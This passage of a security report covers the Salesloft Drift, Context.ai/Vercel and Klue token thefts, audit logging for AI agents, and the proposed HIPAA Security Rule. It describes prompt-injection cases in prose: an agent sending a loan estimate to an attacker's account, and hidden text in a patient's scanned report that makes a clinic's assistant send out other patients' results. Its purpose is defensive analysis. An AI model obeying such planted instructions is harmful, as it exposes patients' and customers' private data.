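Salesloft first indicated that customers who hadn't connected Drift to Salesforce were safe. But on 28 August, Google reported that the thieves had also used tokens for Drift's email feature to read a very small number of mailboxes, and it advised customers to treat every token stored in Drift as compromised. The software company Elastic had received no warning that it was affected, but it checked anyway. It found that its Salesforce records were untouched but that one mailbox had been exposed.

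A company that connects many suppliers takes on the risk of each one. Suppose it has 50, and each has a 1% chance per year of losing its tokens. If the break-ins are independent, the chance of at least one in a year is

1 − 0.99⁵⁰ ≈ 39.5%

The company can't do much about its suppliers' security, but it can limit what each token allows. A website chatbot may need to add a sales contact, but it probably doesn't need to read every support ticket.

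The tickets were valuable to the thieves because customers had pasted passwords and keys into them. Larsen and colleagues believe the thieves mainly wanted these credentials. They searched the stolen text for Amazon access keys, passwords, and tokens for the data-storage company Snowflake.

On 20 August, Salesloft and Salesforce revoked all of Drift's Salesforce tokens. This cut off the attackers' access to Salesforce through Drift, but any other credentials in the stolen data kept working until their owners replaced them. In January 2026, the delivery company Grubhub confirmed a breach and extortion demands. IT Brew's *Forgot about Salesforce data theft?* (2026) relays a report that the attackers were using data from the Drift thefts.

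### How Cloudflare rebuilt the theft

Cloudflare, which provides network and security services for websites, published an unusually detailed account of its own case. It used Drift to let website visitors contact it and Salesforce to manage customer support. Cloudflare (2025) reconstructed these events from its logs:

| Time in August 2025 (UTC) | What the thieves did |
|---|---|
| 9th, 11:51 | Tried to check whether a Cloudflare token worked, and failed |
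| 12th, 22:14 | Logged in to Cloudflare's Salesforce system with Drift's credential and listed the types of record |
| 13th, 19:33 | Looked up the structure of support cases and ran a broad query on them |
| 14th, 00:17 to 11:09 | Counted accounts, contacts and users, studied how staff handle cases, and looked up the limits on automated requests |
| 16th, 19:28 | Counted the support cases |
| 17th, 11:11:56 to 11:15:18 | Exported the text of the cases, using a new network address |
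| 17th, 11:15:42 | Deleted the export job |

Deleting the job removed the main evidence, but Cloudflare could rebuild the sequence of events from the logs that remained. Larsen and colleagues found the same at other companies. Presumably Drift's token allowed the thieves to delete the jobs they had created but not Salesforce's logs. An AI agent should likewise be unable to delete its own log, because an attacker who controls the agent can use all of its permissions.

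The logs were good enough to explain the theft but did not prevent it. The thieves were in the system for more than four and a half days before the export, which took 3 minutes and 22 seconds. Cloudflare didn't learn of the problem until Salesforce and Salesloft told it six days later. An alert for a Drift login from an unfamiliar address could have given Cloudflare days to respond. An alert for a large export would have had to trigger an automatic disconnection, because a person would hardly have had time to act before the export finished.

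Controls on Cloudflare's network could not have blocked the export, because the data went from Salesforce to the thieves' server without passing through that network. Cloudflare now advises companies to monitor traffic between their suppliers but admits that logs of it can be difficult to get. Larsen and colleagues tell victims to ask Salesforce support for the exact queries the thieves ran.

### What Cloudflare found and replaced

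The stolen data included customers' contact details and the subject lines and text of support cases, but no attachments. Cloudflare wrote programs to search this text for its own credentials, looking for strings in a known format and strings random enough to be keys. The programs found 104 Cloudflare API tokens. Cloudflare saw no suspicious use of them but replaced them all.

The text may have held more secrets than the 104 tokens Cloudflare found. Cybernews' *AI agents are leaking their owners’ secrets on GitHub* explains that common scanning tools often miss passwords, because a password can be an ordinary word in an ordinary line of text. Cloudflare also designed its search to find Cloudflare tokens, and customers may have pasted in credentials for other services. Cloudflare therefore told customers to treat anything they had shared in a support case as compromised.

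Cloudflare could do this search because it still had the tickets. A company that deletes its AI assistant's conversations after a month has less data that can be stolen, but if it discovers a theft after two months, it can't search the stolen conversations for passwords. It could scan each conversation for credentials before deleting it and keep only a list of which ones to replace after a theft.

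Cloudflare also removed all Salesloft software, disconnected every outside service from Salesforce and reconnected them with new secrets, which it now changes weekly. A secret stolen at a random moment in the week will work for another three and a half days on average. The thieves at Cloudflare took longer than that, but they could have worked faster, and a thief who is still inside the supplier's systems can steal the replacement too. Cloudflare recommends accepting a supplier's token only from approved network addresses. This would block a copied token used from any other address, but not requests that a thief sends from the supplier's own servers.

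Cloudflare notified its affected customers on 2 September, 16 days after the export. Some attackers now act much faster. In a case that Microsoft disclosed in November 2026, an AI agent found a secret in public code and began copying data from the victim's store of passwords and keys within five minutes of starting its search. The agent took about 28 seconds to correct requests that had failed because they used the wrong version of the interface. Help Net Security's *AI agents now hunt leaked GitHub secrets faster than teams can revoke* (2026) gives the viewpoint of GitGuardian, which sells tools for finding leaked secrets, on the case. The agent searched public code, but an attacker could have an agent search stolen tickets in the same way.

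### Two token thefts in 2026

In April 2026 a smaller AI supplier, Context.ai, caused a breach at Vercel, which hosts websites and applications. Context.ai offered an office product whose agents could act in users' other applications. Its *Security Update* (2026) says that at least one Vercel employee had signed up with a work account and chosen "Allow All" when granting permissions. Vercel's settings appear to have allowed this.

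An intruder at Context.ai stole the token. Vercel (2026) says he used it to take over the employee's Google account and then reach the employee's Vercel account and some internal systems. He then decrypted customers' environment variables, which are settings that often include passwords and keys. The stolen variables weren't marked "sensitive", a Vercel option that prevents anyone from reading a variable's value back. Vercel has since strengthened its defaults.

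Vercel was not a customer of Context.ai, so Vercel's list of approved suppliers would probably not have included it. Besides that list, a company needs an inventory of the tokens its employees have granted, taken from the service that issued them. A proposed US health data rule would require some organisations to map where records move, but the map would be incomplete if it left out connections made through these tokens.

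Context.ai had detected the intruder in March and hired investigators, but it learned only in April, partly from Vercel, that he had probably stolen tokens too. Vercel's logs were more useful because they recorded each time somebody read an environment variable. A wider search of them revealed a few more victims, as well as customer accounts that somebody seemed to have broken into separately. If Vercel had logged only changes to the variables, a thief who only read them would have left much less evidence.

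The other theft, in June 2026, was at Klue, which sells information about competitors to sales teams. Help Net Security's *Klue breach lead to Salesforce data theft, Huntress affected* (2026) reports that the intruders used an old credential created for an abandoned prototype. They added code to Klue's servers and used it to collect customers' tokens for Salesforce, Google Drive, Slack and other services. Klue removed the code and sent customers an alert on 13 June, but the alert didn't identify which of them were affected. Three days later, staff at the security company Huntress received an extortion email with a 48-hour deadline.

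Klue said it had no evidence that the thieves had taken content stored on its own platform, but the tokens let them query the customers' systems directly. By 22 June, at least five cybersecurity companies had confirmed that the breach affected them (Poireault, 2026, *Klue Breach Enables Hackers to Compromise Cybersecurity Firms*).

### What to record when an AI agent moves data

These cases suggest six things to record each time an agent reads, changes or sends data. The last column shows what the log might contain when the procurement assistant emails its summary of a bid.

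| Field | What to record | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Source | Each document the agent used, and its version | Three contracts and a bid received by email |
| Label | Who may read the data, and whether an outsider wrote any of it | Procurement only; untrusted |
| Tool | The operation and whether it succeeded | Send email; succeeded |
| Destination | The exact address and account, and who can read what arrives | Procurement's shared mailbox; 12 employees |
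| Volume | The number of records and their size | One message, six kilobytes |
| Identity | The person, the agent, the token and the network address | The procurement officer; the assistant; token 417; the office network |

A log's identity field needs several parts because the thieves who stole from Cloudflare used Drift's genuine credential. Their requests would have looked normal in a log that recorded only "Drift", but the network addresses showed that they came from somewhere new. If an agent acts under an employee's name, investigators also need to know which actions the agent took. Anthropic gives each Claude Cowork virtual machine its own token for the session, with narrower permissions than the user's. Revoking this token doesn't lock the user out.

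The logged destination has to include the account, because the loan estimate stolen through Claude Cowork went to the attacker's account on an approved domain. Logging volume helps detect bulk exports, but not the theft of something as short as an account number. A company can use the source to determine whom to notify. Software such as FIDES already computes labels before each tool call, so saving them takes little extra work.

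All log entries for one user request should carry the same number. Otherwise an investigator may see that the assistant read a bid at 14:01 and sent an email at 14:02 without knowing whether the two were connected. The log should also include failed and refused calls, because they can reveal an attack before it succeeds. For example, the attempt to check a Cloudflare token failed three days before the first login.

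The log shouldn't contain passwords or copies of the documents, because that would make it another target, as Bain's log of login tokens was. Each document's number and a digital fingerprint of its text are enough to identify what the agent read, as long as the company keeps the original.

### Thefts that look like ordinary work

At Cloudflare, the thieves connected from an unusual network address. That clue is missing when an AI agent is deceived, because the agent uses its usual address, token and tools. Anthropic warns that in such cases there is "no after-the-fact signal to find".

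This is true of a log that records each call by itself. If the entries are linked and labelled, an investigator can look for requests in which the agent read an outsider's text and then sent private data to somebody new. But many legitimate requests fit this description. Suppose 1,000 of an assistant's 20,000 monthly messages fit it, and one of those is a theft. At two minutes each, checking all 1,000 would take about 33 hours. Restricting the search to recipients the company has never dealt with would save most of that time, but it would miss stolen data sent to a bidder who is already a supplier.

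Anthropic therefore prefers to inspect what a tool returns before the model reads it. A small, fast model can do this, though it adds delay and sometimes misses attacks. Checking labels before each call is another way to act before the data leaves.

Isolation can also hide an agent's activity. Security software on an employee's computer can't inspect what happens inside Claude Cowork's virtual machine, which appears as a single program. Anthropic acknowledges that retrieving Cowork's event logs afterwards isn't live monitoring. An export as fast as Cloudflare's would finish before anyone checked the logs. A company could have the virtual machine send out events as they happen, but those records would be less trustworthy if an attacker had taken control of the machine.

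### Leaks without an attacker

Agents can also disclose credentials when nobody is trying to steal them. *'I leaked secrets'* (Udinmwen, November 2026) describes cases from the security company NordLayer. During a routine code review, an AI coding assistant couldn't find its configuration file, so it read all of the computer's environment variables and exposed live passwords. According to its own output, an assistant also leaked passwords for working systems and tokens for a personnel system after reading entire configuration files over ten sessions.

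NordLayer sells AI Scout, which monitors employees' use of AI tools and can block sensitive text before they submit it (TechRadar's *'What companies are facing today is an AI zoo'*). It therefore has a commercial interest in publicising such cases. A few examples also can't show how common these cases are.

Other security companies have found similar leaks on a larger scale. Tom's Hardware's *AI agents inadvertently leak 13,000+ internal screenshots from 300 organizations* reports Glow's findings. Programmers often attach screenshots to a proposed change so that colleagues can review it, but GitHub's command-line tool couldn't attach images in private projects, so agents put the images in public projects and linked to them. A log that recorded only the domain would show a normal upload to GitHub, so it would also need to record who could read the images to show that they were public.

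Apiiro, another security vendor, found 2,539 secrets in public copies of a Claude Code settings file. Cybernews explains that when a programmer approves a command and chooses not to be asked again, Claude Code saves the whole command, including any password in it. In 539 of the 1,105 affected projects, Claude had helped write the change that published the file. Anthropic said it was looking into ways to prevent this.

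An audit log can show that such a leak has happened before, but the agent won't necessarily learn from it. Udinmwen reports that the agents lacked institutional memory and ignored past warnings. So after the first leak, a company has to change what the agent can reach, for example by moving passwords out of the configuration files it reads and into a separate service that signs in for it.

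## The proposed US health data rule: a map of where records move

To limit what an agent can reach, an organisation first has to know where its data is and how it moves. In January 2025 the US Department of Health and Human Services (HHS) proposed the *HIPAA Security Rule to Strengthen the Cybersecurity of Electronic Protected Health Information*, which would require health organisations to keep a written inventory of their technology and a map of how patients' electronic records move, along with many other security measures.

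The Security Rule dates from 2003 and implements a 1996 law, the Health Insurance Portability and Accountability Act (HIPAA). It applies to health insurers, most doctors and hospitals, the clearinghouses that process their transactions, and the suppliers that handle records for any of them. HHS last revised it in 2013.

The proposal isn't law yet. Public comments closed on 7 March 2025, and HHS had planned to finish the rule by May 2026. McDermott's *Final action on HIPAA Security Rule modifications now projected for July 2027* (2026) reports that the government's regulatory agenda now lists the rule as a "long-term action", with final action expected in July 2027. Davis Wright Tremaine's *HHS Updates HIPAA Rulemaking Timeframes* (2026) cautions that this date is only a projection.

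HHS finished a different HIPAA rule in November 2026, on patients' access to their records. National Law Review's *United States Department of Health and Human Services Finalizes Major HIPAA Privacy* explains that this rule, which some people have called a security update, leaves the Security Rule unchanged and that the security proposal is still pending. The access rule took nearly six years from proposal to publication, according to National Law Review's *Focus on Access to PHI*, so July 2027 may be optimistic for the security rule. If HHS publishes it then, most duties would start 240 days later, in early 2028. HHS says the current rule remains in effect in the meantime.

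### What the proposal would require

The current rule calls some measures, including encryption, "addressable". An organisation can decide that such a measure isn't reasonable for it, document why, and use an alternative if a reasonable one exists. HHS found that many organisations treated these measures as optional, so it proposes to make nearly all of them mandatory.

The inventory would list the name, version, location and responsible person for each piece of hardware, software and data. It would include equipment that holds no records but that an intruder could use to reach them. HHS's example is an internet-connected heating control that still has its default password.

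The map would show how records enter an organisation's systems, move through them and leave, and how people access them from outside. An organisation would include its suppliers on the map but leave their own servers out of its inventory. If a clinic uses a cloud record system, both the clinic and the system's supplier would list it, because both have control over the records in it. Organisations would have to update the inventory and the map at least once a year, and after events such as the introduction of new software, an upgrade or a security incident.

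The other main duties are:

| Duty | What the proposed text requires |
|---|---|
| Encryption | Encrypt records in storage and in transit, with exceptions such as some medical devices |
| Separated networks | Divide systems in a "reasonable and appropriate" way, and limit access to records to authorised workstations |
| Multi-factor login | Ask users for at least two kinds of proof, such as a password and a smart card |
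| Supplier checks | Each year, obtain an expert's written analysis of the supplier's technical safeguards and a certification that it is accurate |
| Testing | Scan for known flaws every six months and carry out a mock attack every year |
| Activity records | Record and monitor all activity in real time, and alert staff to signs of unauthorised use |

In 2003, HHS considered requiring an inventory but assumed that organisations would make one anyway when they analysed their risks. Its investigators have since found that many don't know where all their records are. In audits in 2016 and 2017, only 14% of 166 insurers, providers and clearinghouses, and 17% of 41 suppliers, substantially met their duty to analyse risks.

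### AI software in the proposal

The proposed definition of a technology asset covers software and data but doesn't mention AI. In its explanation of the rule, HHS says it would expect the inventory to list any AI software that handles patient records or learns from them. The risk analysis would have to consider what kind of patient information the software can access and how much, who receives that information, and who receives the software's output.

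These questions suit an AI agent well, because they concern what the agent can reach and where its output goes. HHS discusses dangers such as models that reveal personal details from their training data and criminals who use AI to write phishing messages, but not prompt injection. An organisation would still have to identify "all reasonably anticipated threats" to its records, and after EchoLeak it would be hard to argue that nobody could anticipate planted instructions.

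### A clinic adds a laboratory assistant

Suppose a clinic buys an AI assistant that summarises laboratory results. The assistant runs on a server at the clinic and uses a model on its supplier's servers. Most results arrive electronically from one laboratory, but staff also scan in reports that patients bring from elsewhere. By default, the assistant looks up unfamiliar tests on the web, and nobody at the clinic has noticed this.

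The new entries in the inventory might look like this:

| Asset | Version | Person responsible | Location |
|---|---|---|---|
| Laboratory assistant | 2.1 | Lead physician | Clinic server |
| Access token that lets the assistant read results | Issued 3 May | IT contractor | Clinic server |
| Stored summaries | Updated daily | Practice manager | Cloud record system |

The proposed text doesn't mention access tokens, but the Salesloft Drift thefts are a good reason to list them. The map would need five new arrows:

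1. Results and scanned reports go from the record system to the assistant.
2. The assistant sends them to the supplier's model.
3. The summary comes back and goes into the patient's record.
4. Doctors open summaries from home.
5. The web lookup sends search terms and page requests to outside sites.

The practice manager could draw the first four arrows on the map from the supplier's brochure, but she would probably miss the fifth. An attacker could exploit it by registering as a patient and bringing in a report with hidden text that makes the assistant send out other patients' results in a web address.

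### Which duties would expose the web lookup

The mapping requirement could reveal the lookup before any data was stolen, but only if somebody checked which connections the assistant makes. The clinic could run the assistant on invented patient records for a week and record its network traffic. The proposed text requires an accurate map but doesn't prescribe a check like this. If the lookup ran on the supplier's servers, the clinic couldn't see the traffic and would have to rely on the supplier's account.

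The clinic would also have to evaluate the assistant in writing before installing it. That evaluation is a good time to ask about web access. If the supplier added the lookup in a later update, the clinic would have to review the map again, but might not realise that the update had changed where data could go.

Activity records are most likely to reveal the lookup once the assistant is using it, because the clinic would have to record every transmission of patient data. The real-time alerts may not help, since they depend on what the clinic defines as unauthorised in its risk analysis, and the clinic has approved the assistant. HHS suggests a small organisation might have staff review its logs by hand several times a week, which would be too slow to stop an export as fast as the one at Cloudflare.

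In the yearly mock attack, a tester would find the problem by planting an instruction in a sample report. HHS's cost estimate allows an average of three hours for the whole test, so many testers probably wouldn't try this.

The remaining duties would do little to expose the lookup:

- **Encryption** stops others from reading the data on its way, but the attacker's server is the intended recipient and can decrypt it.
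- **Multi-factor login** checks the doctor's identity, and the doctor really has signed in.
- **Closing unused network ports**, another proposed duty, wouldn't help if the lookup used the same port as the connection to the model.
- **The supplier's yearly certification** covers safeguards such as encryption and login, and doesn't test whether the model follows instructions in a scanned report.

Separating the networks could block the theft if the assistant's server could connect only to the record system and the model. But the clinic could argue that its separation was reasonable even if the server still had open access to the web, since the proposed text doesn't specifically require a list of permitted outbound addresses.

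A clinic could therefore carry out all these duties and still lose records to a deceived agent. Even if it found the lookup and drew it on the map, data could leave that way until somebody turned the lookup off or restricted it. Stolen data could also leave by a route the clinic had approved on the map, as it did through Anthropic's own address in the Claude Cowork attack. HHS might argue that the clinic had failed in its general duty to reduce risks to a reasonable level, but only after the records had been stolen.

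The map is still useful. A doctor who sees an arrow from patient records to the open web is likely to ask why it is there. If a supplier reports a break-in, the clinic can use the map to look up which records that supplier receives and which tokens to revoke.

The proposal would also require written procedures for giving each person and each piece of technology only the access its work requires. This less prominent duty might protect the clinic's patients more than the map would. If the assistant's token worked only for the patient whose record was open, the attacker who brought in the report could steal only his own results.

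### What it would cost, and who objects

HHS's main reason for the proposal is the growth in breaches. Organisations reported 302 breaches that each affected at least 500 people in 2018, and 626 in 2022. Over the same period, the number of people affected each year by breaches of any size rose from 12.5 million to 42 million.

HHS estimates that compliance would cost about $9 billion in the first year and $6 billion in each of the next four. About half of the first-year cost would fall on employers that sponsor health plans. For a small clinic, HHS's average figures add up to 19.5 hours of work and about $2,400 in the first year.

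That total excludes the cost of the inventory and the map. HHS regards them as part of the risk analysis organisations already have to do, and says the extra cost is hard to quantify. But its audits suggest many organisations would be starting almost from nothing, so the real cost to them would be higher.

According to HHS, the rule would pay for itself if it reduced the number of people affected by breaches by 7 to 16%. This break-even figure doesn't show that the rule would achieve such a reduction. HHS also uses industry reports to estimate that measures such as encryption and mock attacks would cut the cost of large breaches by 23.6%. Organisations that already have these measures would save less.

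Becker's Hospital Review's *The hospital cyber crackdown explained* describes the opposition to the rule. The American Hospital Association wants the requirements to be voluntary and particularly objects to having to plan for restoring critical systems within 72 hours of losing them. A coalition led by the Medical Group Management Association and CHIME, an association of health technology executives, asked the government to withdraw the proposal.

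Brian Arnold of Huntress predicted in InformationWeek's *New Cybersecurity Rules Coming for Health Care* that people would object to the money and staff required. Shawn Hodges, who runs a network of pharmacies, replied that the industry had similar fears when HIPAA was new, and that the rules exist to protect patients. HHS says a small provider could meet the requirements by using a cloud record system or hiring an outside IT firm. Either option would save the provider work but give another supplier access to its records.

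HHS has the better argument about voluntary measures, because it has published free guidance for years and most of the organisations it audited still fell short. The objection about resources is stronger. HHS estimates that separating an organisation's networks takes an average of 4.5 hours, which may be enough for a small clinic but looks far too low for a hospital with thousands of connected devices. HHS says it based its cost estimates on expert judgement, and it asked the public for better data.

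### The European duties

Like the current US rule, European law gives organisations more freedom to choose their security measures than the proposal would. Article 32 of the General Data Protection Regulation (GDPR) requires security appropriate to the risk, taking cost into account, and lists encryption and regular testing as examples. Article 30 requires many organisations to keep a written record of how they use personal data, including the categories of people and companies that receive it. An entry such as "IT suppliers" could satisfy this requirement without showing the route the data takes.

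Under Article 33, an organisation must report a breach to its data protection regulator within 72 hours of becoming aware of it, where feasible, unless the breach is unlikely to put people at risk. If an AI agent is tricked into sending out records and nobody notices, the 72 hours do not start. A supplier must tell its customer about a breach without undue delay.

The EU's AI Act addresses attacks on models more directly. Article 15 requires high-risk AI systems to withstand outsiders' attempts to change their behaviour by exploiting weaknesses. The attacks it lists include inputs designed to make a model err and attacks on confidentiality, which together seem to cover a report with hidden instructions. But Article 15 doesn't apply yet. The National Law Review's *EU Digital Omnibus on AI Enters Into Force* (2026) gives the new start dates as 2 December 2027 for systems in listed sensitive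 uses, such as hiring, and 2 August 2028 for AI in products that already have to meet EU safety rules. If the clinic were in Europe, its assistant might not count as high-risk, but the GDPR would already apply to the patients' results.
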